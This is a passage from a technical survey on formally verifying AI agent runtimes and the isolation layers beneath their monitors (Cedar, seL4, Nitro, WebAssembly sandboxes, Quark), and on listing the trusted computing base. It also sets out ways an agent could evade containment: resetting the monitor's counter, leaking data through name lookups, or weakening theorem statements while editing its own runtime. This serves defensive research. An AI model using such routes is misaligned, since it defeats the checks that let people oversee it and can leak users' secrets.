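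According to McCann's limitations section, the tests did not reach the BEAM runtime directly, which contradicts this account. But the missing entry was from the runtime's own table, which suggests that the tests reached at least that part of the runtime.

If 10,000 independent inputs produce no disagreement, the true disagreement rate is below about 1 in 3,300 with 95 per cent confidence. This figure applies only to inputs like those the generator produces, but an agent under an attacker's influence may propose a rare sequence that the generator never tried. McCann compares the evidence with that for seL4, but the seL4 group proved that its C code follows the specification, which is much stronger evidence than testing.

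### Cedar: a proved model and a separate Rust program

AWS's policy language Cedar also relies on tests to link a proof to code, on a larger scale. *How We Built Cedar* (Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues, 2024) explains that the developers wrote a simple, executable model of the language in Lean and proved properties of it, including that "forbid" rules always override "permit" rules. They then wrote the production version separately in Rust.

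| Component | Lean model (lines) | Lean proofs (lines) | Rust production code (lines) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Evaluator and authorizer | 897 | 347 | 4,877 |
| Validator | 532 | 4,686 | 6,702 |
| Parser | none | none | 4,114 |
| Shared sets and maps | 244 | 681 | none |
| Total | 1,673 | 5,714 | 15,693 |

Differential random testing compares the two versions. A program generates policies, data and requests, gives the same input to both versions, and reports any difference in their answers. The developers run each group of tests for six hours every day, trying millions of inputs for most groups.

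To generate test inputs, the developers first create a schema, then data that fits it, and then policies and requests that use the data. If the generator chose policies, data and requests independently, most policies would refer to things that don't exist, and the tests would mainly exercise the error handling. A second generator produces policies with type errors, so that the tests also cover those.

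A runtime with memory needs even more carefully generated test inputs. Suppose a tester gives the file agent random proposals, half of them posts, and picks each host at random from 100 names. The chance that three proposals in a row are all posts to api.example.org is (1/200)³, or one in eight million, so short random runs would almost never test the limit of two posts.

Disselkoen and colleagues found four bugs while writing the proofs and 21 through testing. They found ten of the 21 by comparing the Rust code with the Lean models, and the other 11 by testing the Rust code alone. According to a luxas.dev presentation on Cedar, these methods missed nine other bugs, and the project releases a new version only if the tests pass.

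The parser has no Lean model. The developers test it by printing a policy as text, parsing the text and checking that they get the same policy back. If the printer and the parser made matching mistakes, this test would still pass.

Disselkoen and colleagues considered running Lean code in production, which would have let them prove the production code equivalent to the model. They decided against it because few programmers know Lean, it lacks useful libraries, and its compiler produces C code that is hard to debug. They also thought that tools for verifying Rust directly weren't ready. Speed can't have been the reason for choosing Rust over Lean for the authorizer, because the Lean version took a median of 6 microseconds in the tests and the Rust version took 10, although the Rust code also produces more detailed diagnostics.

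Cedar's developers still work this way. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) applies the method to tools that analyse policies, for example to check whether a policy denies every request. Modelling and proving five such analyses took one working day. The analyses still depend on an unverified solver, the program that decides whether a logical formula can be true.

### Hazmat: a checked design and separate code

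Hazmat is an open-source tool that runs coding agents under a separate user account, away from the user's keys and credentials. Its repository, as listed by Ecosyste.ms (2026), describes it as "TLA+ verified". TLA+ is a language for specifying how a system should behave. According to Help Net Security's *Hazmat*, about 5.5 per cent of the code is TLA+ specification, and the program that users install is written separately in Go, "with its own bugs".

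*A primer on formal verification and TLA+* (Vanlightly, 2023) explains that a TLA+ specification models a system's design, not its implementation. Developers usually check it with a model checker, which searches all the interactions possible in a model of limited size and can find serious design errors. On macOS, for example, Hazmat backs up the project, builds a sandbox policy, switches to the agent's account and then starts the agent, with a firewall rule already in place. A model could show that no order of events lets the agent start before the restrictions apply. But if the Go program ignored an error from the firewall and carried on, the agent would have network access even though the design was correct.

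Recording what the real program does and comparing it with the specification strengthens the connection between the proof and the program. Belay is a project written in Elixir and SQL that runs jobs under a spending limit. Its developers checked a model with five jobs and about 188 million distinct states, and found no violations. They also record runs of the real code and use a program to check every event against the specification. Belay's *Formal verification and trace evidence* states that this does not prove the implementation is free of bugs. A recorded run can reveal only mismatches that occur during that run.

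The links differ in which errors they can detect. Suppose the file agent's code contains one of these two errors:

| Link | Programmer writes *n* ≤ 2, not *n* < 2 | Compiler mistranslates correct code |
|---|---|---|
| Code compiled or extracted from a verified source | the proof fails | the proof still succeeds |
| Separate code with differential tests | found if some test makes a third post | found if some test makes a third post |
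| Separate code with recorded runs | found if a recorded run makes a third post | found if a recorded run makes a third post |
| Separate code without a comparison | not found | not found |

Tests run the compiled program, so they can expose compiler errors that a proof about source code would miss. Developers can use both, as McCann does and as Moon and Varshney do on a smaller scale.

### Proofs about the executable itself

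A proof about the compiled code would remove the compiler from the list of trusted components. *Foundational Refinement Proofs for EVM Bytecode, at the Price of Tokens* (2026) describes a Lean framework for such proofs about smart contracts, which are programs that run on a blockchain. A language-model agent uses the framework to prove that a contract's bytecode refines a high-level specification. The proof does not depend on which compiler produced the bytecode.

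Proofs could also replace the random tests that compare a simple model with a faster program. In *Agentic Verified Optimization of Real-World Software* (2026), agents search for a faster implementation and a proof that it is equivalent to the original. Some of the faster programs reorder computations or avoid building intermediate data. For Cedar, this would mean optimising the Lean version itself, and the practical objections to running Lean in production would remain.

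Developers of agent systems have begun to narrow the same gap. *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies in Multi-Agent Large Language Model Systems* (2026) treats the lack of runnable code as the main weakness of its verified models. It therefore adds a Rust implementation of one of them, tests it with real language models and links it to the proof by a mechanised refinement.

For a Python runtime such as the compiled PocketFlow, a proof about the executable would need a formal semantics of Python's bytecode and of every library function that the runtime calls. It would also require trusting or verifying the bytecode interpreter, which is a much larger program than the dispatch loop.

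## Verified isolation beneath the monitor

A monitor is tamper-proof, as Anderson required, only if the agent's code cannot write to the monitor's memory. Suppose the file agent runs a script that the model wrote, and the script can write to the runtime's memory. After two posts, the script sets *n* back to 0, and the monitor allows a third. The monitor followed its rules, but the containment proof relied on *n* changing only as those rules prescribe. A script with direct access to the network card could bypass the monitor and post without changing *n*.

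An isolation layer below the monitor has to prevent the agent's code from accessing devices or the monitor's memory. This layer may be an operating-system kernel, a hypervisor (software that runs several virtual machines on one computer) or a compiler that adds checks to untrusted code.

### What each proof assumes of the other

The two proofs form an assume-guarantee pair, in which the runtime's proof assumes what the isolation layer's theorem guarantees. For the file agent, with P as the policy:

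The runtime proof assumes that other code never changes the monitor's program, policy or counters (A1), and that other code reaches files and the network only by sending the monitor a proposal (A2). Under these assumptions, it guarantees that every trace satisfies P and that the monitor never gives its own access rights away.

Isolation layer's theorem
  assumes     The system starts with the right access rights, and
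              the monitor never gives its own away.
  guarantees  A1 and A2.
```

Each proof assumes something that the other guarantees, but induction on the steps keeps the argument from being circular. If A1 and A2 have held up to some step, the monitor is intact and gives nothing away in that step, so the isolation theorem ensures that A1 and A2 still hold afterwards. Only the assumption about the starting access rights remains.

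The runtime proof holds even if a script garbles a proposal on its way to the monitor, because the result is another proposal and the unconstrained oracle already allows every proposal. The three original clauses also hold if the agent's code uses up all the processor time, because a monitor that cannot run sends nothing. A secrecy theorem also requires the layer below to stop the agent's code from reading memory that holds secrets.

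### EROS: an early containment theorem

Shapiro and Weber proved a guarantee of this kind in *Verifying the EROS Confinement Mechanism* (2000). In the EROS operating system, a program can act on an object, such as a page of memory, only if it holds a capability, an unforgeable token that names the object and the operations its holder may perform on it. A program can gain more capabilities only through the ones it already has.

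EROS used capabilities to address Lampson's confinement problem. Before handing over data, a customer can ask a trusted program, the constructor, whether a new service could leak it. The constructor checks the service's initial capabilities for any that would let it write to the outside without the customer's authorisation. Read access can also allow leaks, because a readable object may contain a capability that permits writing. EROS therefore has "weak" capabilities, which make any capability fetched through them weak and read-only too.

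Shapiro and Weber wrote an operational semantics for a broad class of capability systems. They derived the set of objects a confined program could ever change from the starting capabilities, and proved that no sequence of operations changes anything outside that set. The theorem has the same form as the file agent's, with the kernel as the monitor, and it holds whatever the confined program attempts. If a script starts with only its own memory and a capability to send proposals to the monitor, every outside change it causes must go through the monitor.

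The theorem concerns a model of the architecture, not the EROS code, and does not cover covert channels. Its proof was on paper. Doerrie later checked a confinement proof for capability systems in the proof assistant Coq, now called Rocq.

### seL4: from the specification to the C code

*seL4* (Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues, 2009) extended proof to the code of a complete kernel. seL4 is a microkernel, so only a minimal set of functions, such as memory protection, threads and communication between programs, runs with full control of the hardware. File systems and device drivers run as ordinary programs, and capabilities determine what each program may access.

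The proof connects three descriptions of the kernel. An abstract specification gives the effect of each system call, an executable specification adds data structures and algorithms, and the C code is compiled and run. Klein and colleagues proved by forward simulation that each description refines the one above it. User programs are the kernel's counterpart to the unconstrained oracle. The proof models them as steps that may change any memory open to them, so it covers all their possible behaviour, whether "benign, buggy, or malicious".

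| Part of the 2009 project | Size or effort |
|---|---|
| C code | 8,700 lines |
| Assembly code | 600 lines |
| Isabelle proof | 200,000 lines |
| Design and programming of the kernel | 2.2 person-years |
| Proof work specific to seL4 | 11 person-years |
| Proof tools and libraries | about 9 person-years |

Trustworthy Systems, the group behind seL4, puts the verified part of the C code at 7,500 lines. The other 1,200 lines boot the kernel. Klein and colleagues also assumed that the assembly code, compiler, cache management and hardware were correct, and considered only a single processor.

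Much of the work went into more than 150 invariants, which serve the same purpose as the file agent's statement that *n* equals the number of Sent events. Before the C verification, student projects and work on another processor had exposed 16 defects. The verification found another 144. Many were typos, but some could crash the kernel or create a security hole.

Changes took a lot of proof work when they affected many invariants. One new system call took a day to design and program and less than a week to prove. Adding interrupts, page tables and address spaces required 1.5 to 2 person-years of further proof. An agent runtime probably changes much more often than a microkernel, which is a good reason to keep the isolation layer separate and avoid changing it.

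Functional correctness means that the code does what its specification describes, but the specification might still allow one program to interfere with another. In 2009, the proof about seL4's access control covered only a high-level model that was not linked to the code. Sewell and colleagues supplied an integrity proof in 2011, and Murray and colleagues followed with an information-flow proof in 2013. A1 needs integrity, which prevents a program from changing data without authorisation.

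The information-flow proof was harder to extend to the code, because refinement does not always preserve secrecy. Suppose a specification lets the kernel return either 0 or 1. Code that returns the first bit of another program's key is a valid refinement, since both values are permitted, but it leaks the bit. Murray and colleagues had to remove such choices from the specification. Anyone proving secrecy for an agent runtime faces the same problem wherever the specification permits more than one reply.

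### The kernel's conditions and its present coverage

The security theorems also depend on how the system is set up. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* explains that integrity requires isolated components to have no write access to each other, and that confidentiality holds between the scheduler's security domains, not between arbitrary threads. In some configurations, a verified initialiser reads a description of the intended capabilities and sets up the system to match. This initialiser could supply the starting condition in the assume-guarantee pair. Without such a step, a verified kernel does not guarantee that the system on top of it enforces isolation, as Andronick emphasises in *What's verified, what's not, and what does it mean*.

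The proofs have since been extended to other processors, some more completely than others. The table combines the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations* with two sources that are more recent or more detailed, the Foundation's *seL4 News* and Trustworthy Systems' *The seL4 verification project*.

| Processor family | Functional correctness | Integrity and confidentiality | Compiled machine code |
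|---|---|---|---|
| 32-bit Arm | yes | yes, in one configuration | yes, in one configuration |
| 64-bit Arm | yes | yes, completed in 2026 | not listed |
| 64-bit RISC-V | yes | yes | yes, according to Trustworthy Systems |
| 64-bit x86 | yes, without the optimised fast path | not listed | not listed |

Many servers that run agents have x86 processors, for which seL4 has the fewest proofs. Heiser (2026) adds in *seL4* that the verification still applies to only one processor core and that timing channels remain open. The proofs have grown to well over a million lines by his count.

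Another exclusion directly affects A2. A network card or disk controller can often write to memory without going through the processor. Hardware called an IOMMU restricts which addresses each device can reach, but no verified configuration of seL4 accounts for it. An agent's script that controls such a device might overwrite the monitor even though the kernel's theorem still holds. Giving the script no control over these devices avoids this, but the drivers that control them must then be trusted.

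According to the seL4 Foundation, nobody has found a functional-correctness defect in the verified code since 2009. Small defects have turned up in every unverified part, including the boot code and the assumptions about hardware and compilers. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Version 16.0.0 Release* (2026) describes two that also affected verified configurations, both in code that the proofs assume to be correct. On 32-bit Arm, a program with sufficient capabilities could crash the system through a cache operation. On Arm processors in hypervisor mode, the kernel did not properly save and restore one register when switching between programs, so one program could overwrite another's value.

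The same release fixed a more dangerous error in an unverified x86 configuration, where a virtual machine working with its own monitor program could run code inside the kernel. For version 17.0.0, developers audited the unproved code in verified configurations, and the seL4 Foundation thanks Anthropic for reporting some of the problems fixed in that release. This record is good evidence for the proofs, and it suggests that an attacker should look for errors in unproved code.

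### The Nitro Isolation Engine

AWS has brought verified isolation to a commercial cloud. Its Nitro Hypervisor creates and schedules virtual machines and decides how to allocate resources. On servers with Graviton5 processors, the hypervisor no longer has direct access to customers' virtual machines. It must go through a smaller component beneath it, the Nitro Isolation Engine, which checks every request that touches a machine's state. Amazon Science's *EC2’s formally verified “isolation engine” provides mathematical assurance of virtual-machine isolation* compares this component to a separation kernel, a minimal program, first proposed in 1981, that enforces isolation and leaves all other decisions to the software above it.

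The engine is written in a restricted subset of Rust, for which the AWS team defined a semantics in Isabelle. Each operation's specification states what must hold before it runs and what will hold afterwards. If a virtual processor sends a request to turn itself on, for example, the engine must return the error "AlreadyOn" and leave everything else unchanged. The team proved that the verified operations meet their specifications, always finish and cause no memory errors. For secrecy, they proved a form of noninterference that lets information out only where the design declassifies it. Integrity means that operations on one virtual machine do not affect another's private state.

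The announcements are less clear about how much of the engine the proofs cover. In *Nitro Isolation Engine*, Mulligan (2025) reported about 260,000 lines of models and proofs and wrote that the engine behaves as specified "for all operations". In a 2026 conference abstract, Chong, Dockins and colleagues report 330,000 lines but describe a narrower scope. They say the proofs cover the core operations for managing virtual machines, power management, various utility calls and part of the handling of memory faults and other aborts. Proofs for the virtual interrupt controller and the management of PCI devices, such as network cards, are still to come.

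The narrower account is more specific and more recent. Saidi agrees in *AWS Nitro Isolation Engine* that verification so far covers the calls that start, run and tear down a virtual machine. He also lists the Rust compiler and the hardware among the assumptions. AWS has published its general proof library and plans to let third parties inspect the engine's source code and proofs. Until then, outsiders must rely on AWS's description of the theorems.

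As with seL4, A1 is better supported than A2, because device management is among the unproved parts. The engine separates virtual machines from each other, so it does not protect a monitor that runs in the same virtual machine as the agent's scripts. An operator would have to put the monitor in a second virtual machine and make it the only route from the agent's virtual machine to the network.

### Verified software sandboxes

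A runtime can also isolate a script without a separate virtual machine by checking the script's machine code before it runs. Google's Native Client did this for programs in the browser. It accepted a program only if every memory access stayed within a fixed region and every jump went to an instruction that the checker had examined. Without the rule about jumps, a program could jump into the middle of a harmless instruction, where the bytes may decode as a forbidden one.

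Morrisett and colleagues built a verified checker for this purpose in *RockSalt* (2012). They modeled a subset of the x86 instruction set in Coq and proved that any program the checker accepts obeys the sandbox policy in that model. The checker was smaller and faster than Google's. It can reject safe programs, which makes it less useful but doesn't affect its soundness.

WebAssembly, a portable code format, has since replaced Native Client. A WebAssembly program has its own block of memory and can reach the outside only through functions that its host provides. This suits an agent runtime because the host could provide just two functions, Read and Post, both of which call the monitor. The isolation then depends on the compiler that turns WebAssembly into machine code. Bosamiya, Lim and Parno (2022) proved in *Provably-Safe Multilingual Software Sandboxing using WebAssembly* that their compiler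 vWasm produces only sandboxed code, whatever program it receives.

A correct compiler does not protect against errors in the host functions. If Read copied a file to an address outside the script's block, it could overwrite the monitor. *WaVe* (Johnson and colleagues, 2023) presents a verified runtime for the standard functions that WebAssembly programs use to access files and the network. The proof shows that these functions preserve memory isolation and restrict each program to the files and network resources it may use. It assumes that the operating system carries out the calls correctly. Ordinary Linux programs must be compiled to WebAssembly before WaVe can run them, which limits its use for coding agents.

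### Quark: a verified kernel for an untrusted browser

*Establishing Browser Security Guarantees through Formal Shim Verification* (Jang, Tatlock and Lerner, 2012) presents Quark, a browser with much the same structure as a contained agent. A browser engine is too large to verify, and attackers regularly find errors in it. Quark runs each tab in a sandbox with its own, almost unchanged copy of the WebKit engine. To fetch a page or use a cookie, a tab has to send a request to a small kernel written and verified in Coq.

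The kernel handles one request at a time, and its specification defines which sequences of system calls it may make in response. The proof allows a tab to send any message. From the specification, Jang and colleagues derived that one tab cannot affect how the kernel treats another, that tabs cannot read or change cookies belonging to other domains, and that the address bar shows the correct address.

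| Quark | Agent runtime |
|---|---|
| WebKit | the model and the scripts it writes |
| a tab's request | an action |
| the browser kernel | the runtime's parser, monitor and adapters |
| a trace of system calls | a trace of events |
| any message from a tab | the unconstrained oracle |

The similarity extends to the layer beneath the monitor. Quark's guarantees depend on the sandbox preventing WebKit from making its own system calls, but neither the sandbox nor the Linux kernel is verified. Quark's proof is therefore the upper half of an assume-guarantee argument, and the lower half would have to prove that the sandbox and kernel enforce this restriction.

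The policies differ more. A browser can keep websites apart because a tab for a bank seldom needs data from a tab for a newspaper. An agent often has to combine data from different sources, for example by reading an invoice in an email and then paying it. Running one isolated model for each source would prevent this work or require a trusted program to pass information between the models. A Quark user also chooses which sites to visit and types into them directly, whereas an agent makes many of these choices for the user. Quark shows that a small verified program can mediate for a large untrusted one, but an agent also needs a policy for combining data from different sources, which browsers mostly avoid doing.

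### What deployed agents rest on

Most agent sandboxes depend on the Linux kernel. A container is a group of ordinary Linux processes with a restricted view of files, other processes and the network, so an error in the kernel they share with the host can let the agent's code escape. gVisor puts a second kernel, which runs as an ordinary program, between the agent's code and Linux. A microVM gives the agent its own kernel, but on Linux servers it usually relies on KVM, the hypervisor built into the host's kernel.

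Mainstream kernels contain tens of millions of lines, and Heiser cites about ten critical exploits a year for Linux. He also estimates that verification effort grows with the square of the specification's size. A kernel with a specification 100 times as large as seL4's would therefore need 10,000 times seL4's original 11 person-years of effort, or 110,000 person-years. Language models now write many proofs, so verification will probably need less human labour, but someone would still have to write and review an enormous specification.

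| Isolation layer | What the agent's code has to get past | Verified parts |
|---|---|---|
| Container | the host's Linux kernel | no proof of isolation as a whole |
| gVisor | gVisor, then the host's kernel | no proof of isolation as a whole |
| Firecracker microVM | Firecracker and KVM | AWS has checked selected Firecracker code |
| EC2 virtual machine on Graviton5 | the Nitro Isolation Engine | core virtual-machine operations |
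| seL4 component | seL4 | depends on the configuration |

Checks on Firecracker, AWS's program for running microVMs, use Kani, a tool that examines every input up to a set size. They cover components such as the I/O limiter, but do not prove that the agent's code stays inside the microVM. Columbia Engineering's *SeKVM* describes a research hypervisor with a security proof. The hypervisor moves the critical part of KVM into a small verified core, but the proof does not apply to the standard KVM on which most microVMs run.

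Operators often stack several of these layers. *Rethinking the confidential cloud through a unified low-level abstraction for composable isolation* (2025), which mentions gVisor as a sandbox for a possibly compromised LLM runtime, objects that each mechanism stops only one kind of attack and adds its own trusted code. Stacking can still help when an attacker has to break two layers in turn, but not when the same kernel error defeats both, or when each layer protects against something different and the attacker needs to defeat only one.

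### Joining the two proofs

No published system appears to join a verified agent runtime to a verified isolation layer in a single theorem, though some come close in one respect. WaVe combines memory isolation with verified access to files and the network, but its verification does not cover the operating system. Veracruz, a framework for computing on data from parties who distrust each other, can run on seL4. The paper reposted on HackerNoon as *the open source privacy project making untrusted devices work together securely* claims that seL4 provides strong isolation, but does not claim a proof of the Veracruz runtime above it.

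For the file agent on seL4, the work might divide as follows:

| Component | Access it needs | What someone must prove |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's scripts | a channel to the monitor | nothing |
| Monitor | channels to the file server and network driver | it follows the three rules |
| File server | the disk | it returns only the file that the monitor requested |
| Network driver | the network card | it sends only what the monitor passes on, once |

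If the language model runs elsewhere, the connection to it also needs its own channel and rule. Otherwise, the agent could use that connection to bypass Post.

The components look small enough to verify. LionsOS, an operating system built on seL4, has a 569-line Ethernet driver. Heiser reports promising early experiments with automated proof on such components. Because seL4 enforces the boundaries between components, developers can verify each one separately.

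seL4's proofs are about memory and capabilities, while the file agent's policy is about FileRead and Sent events, so a linking theorem would still have to show that the network card transmits a message only when the trace contains the corresponding Sent event. If the runtime's proof is in Lean or Dafny and the kernel's is in Isabelle, no single checker can confirm that the assumption in one matches the guarantee in the other. Someone would have to translate the statement by hand or redo one of the proofs. The runtime would also have to run without Linux, or inside a virtual machine with the monitor outside it, and current agent frameworks written in Python expect an ordinary operating system.

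## Listing the trusted computing base

The file agent's containment theorem applies to a real system only if the parser produces well-formed actions, every effect reaches the monitor, the code follows the three rules, and nothing else changes *n*. The components that make these conditions true, and whatever the proof itself depends on, form the trusted computing base (TCB). No tool prints the whole list, but an operator can derive it from the theorem.

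### From hypotheses to components

The derivation has four steps:

1. State the claim about the real world, and write down every hypothesis needed to get from the theorem to that claim.
2. For each hypothesis, name the components that make it true in the deployed system.
3. Suppose that one of these components misbehaves in the worst possible way. If the claim can then be false although the checker still accepts every proof, the component is part of the TCB.
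4. Do the same for whatever that component depends on, such as its compiler.

Suppose the claim about the file agent is that it reads only files under /work, its messages reach only api.example.org, it sends at most two messages, and it sends none after reading keys.txt. One assumption of the proof is that the runtime opens the file whose path the monitor checked, which depends on the path resolver and the operating system. A resolver that misses a symbolic link can make the claim false, so the resolver is on the list of trusted components.

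The code that writes "denied" into the history is not in the trusted computing base (TCB) for this guarantee. Even if it wrote "sent" after every denial, the four clauses would still hold, because the proof covers every history. The same code would be in the TCB for a secrecy theorem, because a reply that varies with a secret can leak it. Each guarantee has its own TCB, so an operator who wants another guarantee has to repeat the steps.

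The list also depends on how the claim is worded. The claim that messages "reach only api.example.org" is true only if that service doesn't pass them on, so the service has to be on the list. A claim that the runtime sends them nowhere else would not require trusting the service, but it would be a weaker guarantee.

### The file agent's list

Suppose that developers write and verify the runtime in Lean, that it runs on Linux, and that people approve each change to the policy. The steps then give this list:

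| Trusted by | Component | Possible failure | Available check |
|---|---|---|---|
| Proof | Proof checker | accepts a false proof | recheck the proof with an independently written checker |
| Proof | Axioms | two axioms contradict each other, so anything is provable | print the axioms that the theorem uses |
| Proof | Definitions | a typing error makes P true of every trace | prove that sample bad traces violate P |
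| Specification | Policy | no clause mentions a copy of keys.txt | prove that P implies a separately written goal |
| Specification | Event types | no event represents a name lookup | record network traffic during tests and match it with events |
| Deployment | Parser and path resolver | /work/../etc/passwd reaches the monitor unresolved | test with random malformed input, or prove the code correct |
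| Deployment | Monitor code | allows a post when *n* = 2 | prove refinement, or test runs with three posts |
| Deployment | Adapters | the HTTP library follows a redirect | test against a server that redirects and times out |
| Deployment | Compiler and language runtime | mistranslate *n* < 2 | test the compiled program, or use a verified compiler |
| Deployment | Operating system | lets another process change *n* | use a verified kernel, and confirm at each start that the sandbox is active |
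| Deployment | Hardware | a device overwrites the monitor's memory | restrict devices with an IOMMU |
| Deployment | Credentials | the runtime accepts a forged certificate, and an impostor receives the messages | accept only the service's known certificate |
| Deployment | Permitted service | api.example.org forwards messages to other hosts | use an account that cannot forward |
| Deployment | Human approvers | someone approves a looser policy without reading it | show the exact change and require a second approver |

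Name lookups are an easy effect to miss. To find the address of 4711.example.net, a computer may pass that name to a server controlled by the owner of example.net. If the runtime looks up the host before the monitor decides, the model can reveal the number 4711 to that owner by proposing a post to 4711.example.net, even if the monitor then denies the post.

Testing a component makes a failure less likely but leaves the component on the list. Proving it correct can remove it, but whatever the new proof depends on takes its place. Some checks also take much more effort than others. Lean prints a theorem's axioms on request, and an unfinished proof shows up there as an extra axiom. Definitions have no similar check, so people have to read them.

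### Why the model is not on the list

Applying the third step to the model means letting an attacker choose everything it outputs. The theorem holds for every oracle, so it already covers this case, and the model stays off the list. Moon and Varshney also leave out the model's prompts, its training and how it chooses actions. A model that writes proofs can stay off the list too, as long as a checker verifies the proofs and people have read the definitions.

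The model belongs in the trusted computing base if the runtime relies on its judgement, even if the same weights are untrusted when they propose actions. When a language model takes the user's place at PerMIT's confirmation gate, or decides whether an email contains personal data, a wrong answer can allow a forbidden effect.

For some guarantees, the list needs a separate entry for the company that runs the model. Each call to the model sends the company the history, which may include the contents of keys.txt. The file agent's clauses do not cover these calls, because a call to the model is not a Sent event. But a claim that the key never leaves the operator's machine would be false after the first call that included it, and a claim that no outsider learns the key would depend on the company.

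### Hypotheses in one list, components in another

Published lists are hard to compare because some contain hypotheses, as in the first step above, and others contain components, as in the second. Dongol gives hypotheses. The theorems about relative security apply to a runtime that satisfies seven of them:

| Assumption | Requirement | Example of a failure |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted execution | a trusted interpreter runs the plan | the model skips a step |
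| Complete mediation | the monitor rules on each of the model's tool calls and untrusted reads, one by one | the agent runs a browser outside the monitor |
| Mediated reads | untrusted content enters the model's context only after the monitor allows the read | the runtime loads a page in advance |
| Silent denials | a denied request has no effect that the attacker can see | the attacker receives an error message |
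| Limited observation | the attacker sees neither the monitor's state nor the agent's internal steps | showing a reply loads an image from the attacker's server |
| Fresh sessions | a new session clears everything the model retains from untrusted content | long-term memory carries text over |
| Trusted channels | the attacker cannot write to the sources of trusted input | a "trusted" calendar accepts invitations from outsiders |

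Much of this list concerns what an attacker can observe, since the theorems are about secrecy. Dongol considers a harness like AgentDojo's, which checks and then executes every call itself, to satisfy complete mediation and mediated reads. The seven assumptions do not include Isabelle, a compiler or an operating system, so an operator still has to identify the components that each assumption depends on.

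Jiang and colleagues list PerMIT's assumptions, what each one contributes and where it is weak. The labels for a text's origin depend on an authenticated channel for the user's commands. The rule that only approval can confer trust depends on the integrity of the memory store and its log, and the approval depends on a display that shows the exact text. Jiang and colleagues consider the assumption that users intend what they approve weakest when users approve a batch at once. Approving a summary requires the stronger assumption that the user has checked it against the sources it cites.

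They also distinguish the theorems, which Lean's kernel checks, from eight example scenarios that rely on Lean's evaluator. A numbered list of modelling differences helps anyone reviewing the definitions see where the Lean version is known to depart from the system on paper, for instance in what happens to an approval when the tool call is aborted.

Sistla and colleagues list Tether's trusted computing base (TCB) as the host's kernel, the system-call tracer, the disposable file layer, the network proxy, the code that infers actions, and Lean's kernel, compiler and runtime. The prototype runs the policy directly in Lean, so the monitor and the proofs share one definition. For higher speed, they suggest a Rust version with differential tests against the Lean one, which would add the Rust program to the TCB.

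The policy is not among these components. That is reasonable for the seven proved invariants, since a policy error that broke one of them would have made its proof fail. Any other property still depends on the policy being correct. The guarantees also depend on files' initial labels. If someone labels the company's inventory Public, Tether lets the agent upload it.

Moon and Varshney mix the two kinds of entry. Their list contains the policy, the relations between abstract and concrete states and events, the assumption that every effect passes through the verified interface, Dafny's verifier and compiler, and the shim. When they describe the deployed system, they add the parser and the code that supplies actions, which they trust only to return values of the right type. They name three ways the deployed guarantee can fail, of which Dafny reports only the first: the refinement proof fails,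 an effect bypasses the interface, or the policy does not express what its author wanted.

David and colleagues give two lists of what must be trusted, and an operator needs both. The list for a deployment contains the monitor, the points where it intercepts effects, and the contract. The list for the theorems contains Lean's kernel, the definitions and the external assumptions. Hempel and colleagues' assumptions for Kairos also mix hypotheses with components. They concern the host, the monitor, the virtual machine's exits and the model's provider.

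### L3M's trust ledger

*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) gives the most detailed account of what each theorem depends on. L3M is an Amazon agent runtime, written in Lean 4, in which agents can create sub-agents and write their own tools.

When an agent starts, L3M creates a capability token for each permission in the agent's grant, such as a token that lists the hosts the agent may contact. Every function that touches files, the network, Git or another process takes a token as an argument, so a tool without the right token cannot express the call. An agent-written tool is a Lean program whose type states which kinds of effect it may have. L3M offers the tool to the agent only if the agent's existing tokens cover those effects.

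This protection would fail if a tool could make its own tokens, so in each build a program called the sealing linter inspects the code after Lean has expanded it. It rejects any token constructed outside the module that defines it, and any file write or process start outside a short list of modules. With few exceptions, it also rejects unsafe code and new axioms.

Eisenach and colleagues trust the person who writes the first grant and answers requests for review. The trusted software consists of Lean's kernel and compiler, six small C files that make system calls, the Linux kernel, four programs that L3M starts (including Git), a fixed set of certificate authorities, and the model provider's API. They also trust the settings and the record of all grants.

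The trust ledger then grades the theorems one by one. A proof may rest on Lean's kernel alone, on compiled evaluation, or on a named assumption, which is a statement about the outside world together with observations that would refute it. A program computes the grade from the proof, so the author cannot overstate it. The main guarantees look like this:

| Guarantee | Basis | What it leaves open |
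|---|---|---|
| A file tool cannot name a path outside the agent's directories | kernel | the theorem concerns the path's text; other code checks symbolic links |
| A new sub-agent's grant never exceeds its parent's | kernel | a person can later grant more |
| L3M creates no token that the grant does not cover | kernel | the build prevents forgery, without a proof |
| Sub-agents cannot spend more than the budget they share | kernel | covers one set of loans, not a whole run |
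| An agent-written program uses only approved constants | kernel | covers only constants that the program names directly |
| Irreversible calls that no token limits always go to review | kernel | holds only under the default review setting |
| L3M can restore an edited file | kernel, and the assumption that Git returns the bytes it stored | changes that have already left the machine |

The budget theorem is an example of a narrow result. It proves that the model calls a parent lends to its sub-agents, plus those it keeps, never exceed its original budget. If a parent with 100 calls lends 30 to one sub-agent and 50 to another, it has at most 20 left. Extending the theorem to a whole run would require an invariant that also covers later loans and returns.

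Eisenach and colleagues also proved, by counterexample, that a descendant's grant can exceed the stored grant of the agent at the top of the tree. This can happen even with the top agent's direct children, because a child may receive access to its parent's own Git branches, which the parent's stored grant does not list. They then proved a weaker bound that allows for these branches.

L3M proves theorems about single checks but none about a whole session. The argument that these checks together contain an agent is informal. Loading an agent-written tool is a particular risk, because Lean can run code while it is processing a program's source. L3M therefore checks the form of the source before loading it, but nobody has proved that malicious source cannot affect the host during loading. The guarantees also do not cover secrecy, so an agent that can read a key could copy it into a file it is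 allowed to publish.

The third step of the procedure puts the sealing linter in the TCB, since an error in it could let a tool forge a token while every theorem still holds. The linter is missing from the paper's main list of trusted code, but other parts of the paper identify as trusted the program that processes Lean source and the code that carries out each kind of effect.

Eisenach and colleagues also describe how an agent could get around the proofs while improving L3M itself. The build fails if a change breaks a theorem, but the agent could weaken the theorem's statement and the build would still succeed. They therefore want someone other than the agent to control the specification and the tests. The same precaution makes sense for any project in which a model writes both code and proofs.

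L3M is designed to ask human approvers less often. Eisenach and colleagues cite a figure that users approve about 93 per cent of Claude Code's permission prompts, which suggests that many approvals involve little thought. In L3M, a second model first reviews any call that L3M cannot undo and that no token restricts, and the agent may defend the call or choose another. A person decides only if the agent and the reviewing model still disagree, which happened for 2.4 per cent of reviewed calls in Eisenach and colleagues' tests.

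### What the lists leave out

The table compares the four lists of trusted components, with David and colleagues' two lists combined.

| Component | PocketFlow proof | Alignment contracts | Tether | L3M |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Proof checker | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| Compiler | yes | no | yes | yes |
| Policy or grant | yes | yes | no | yes |
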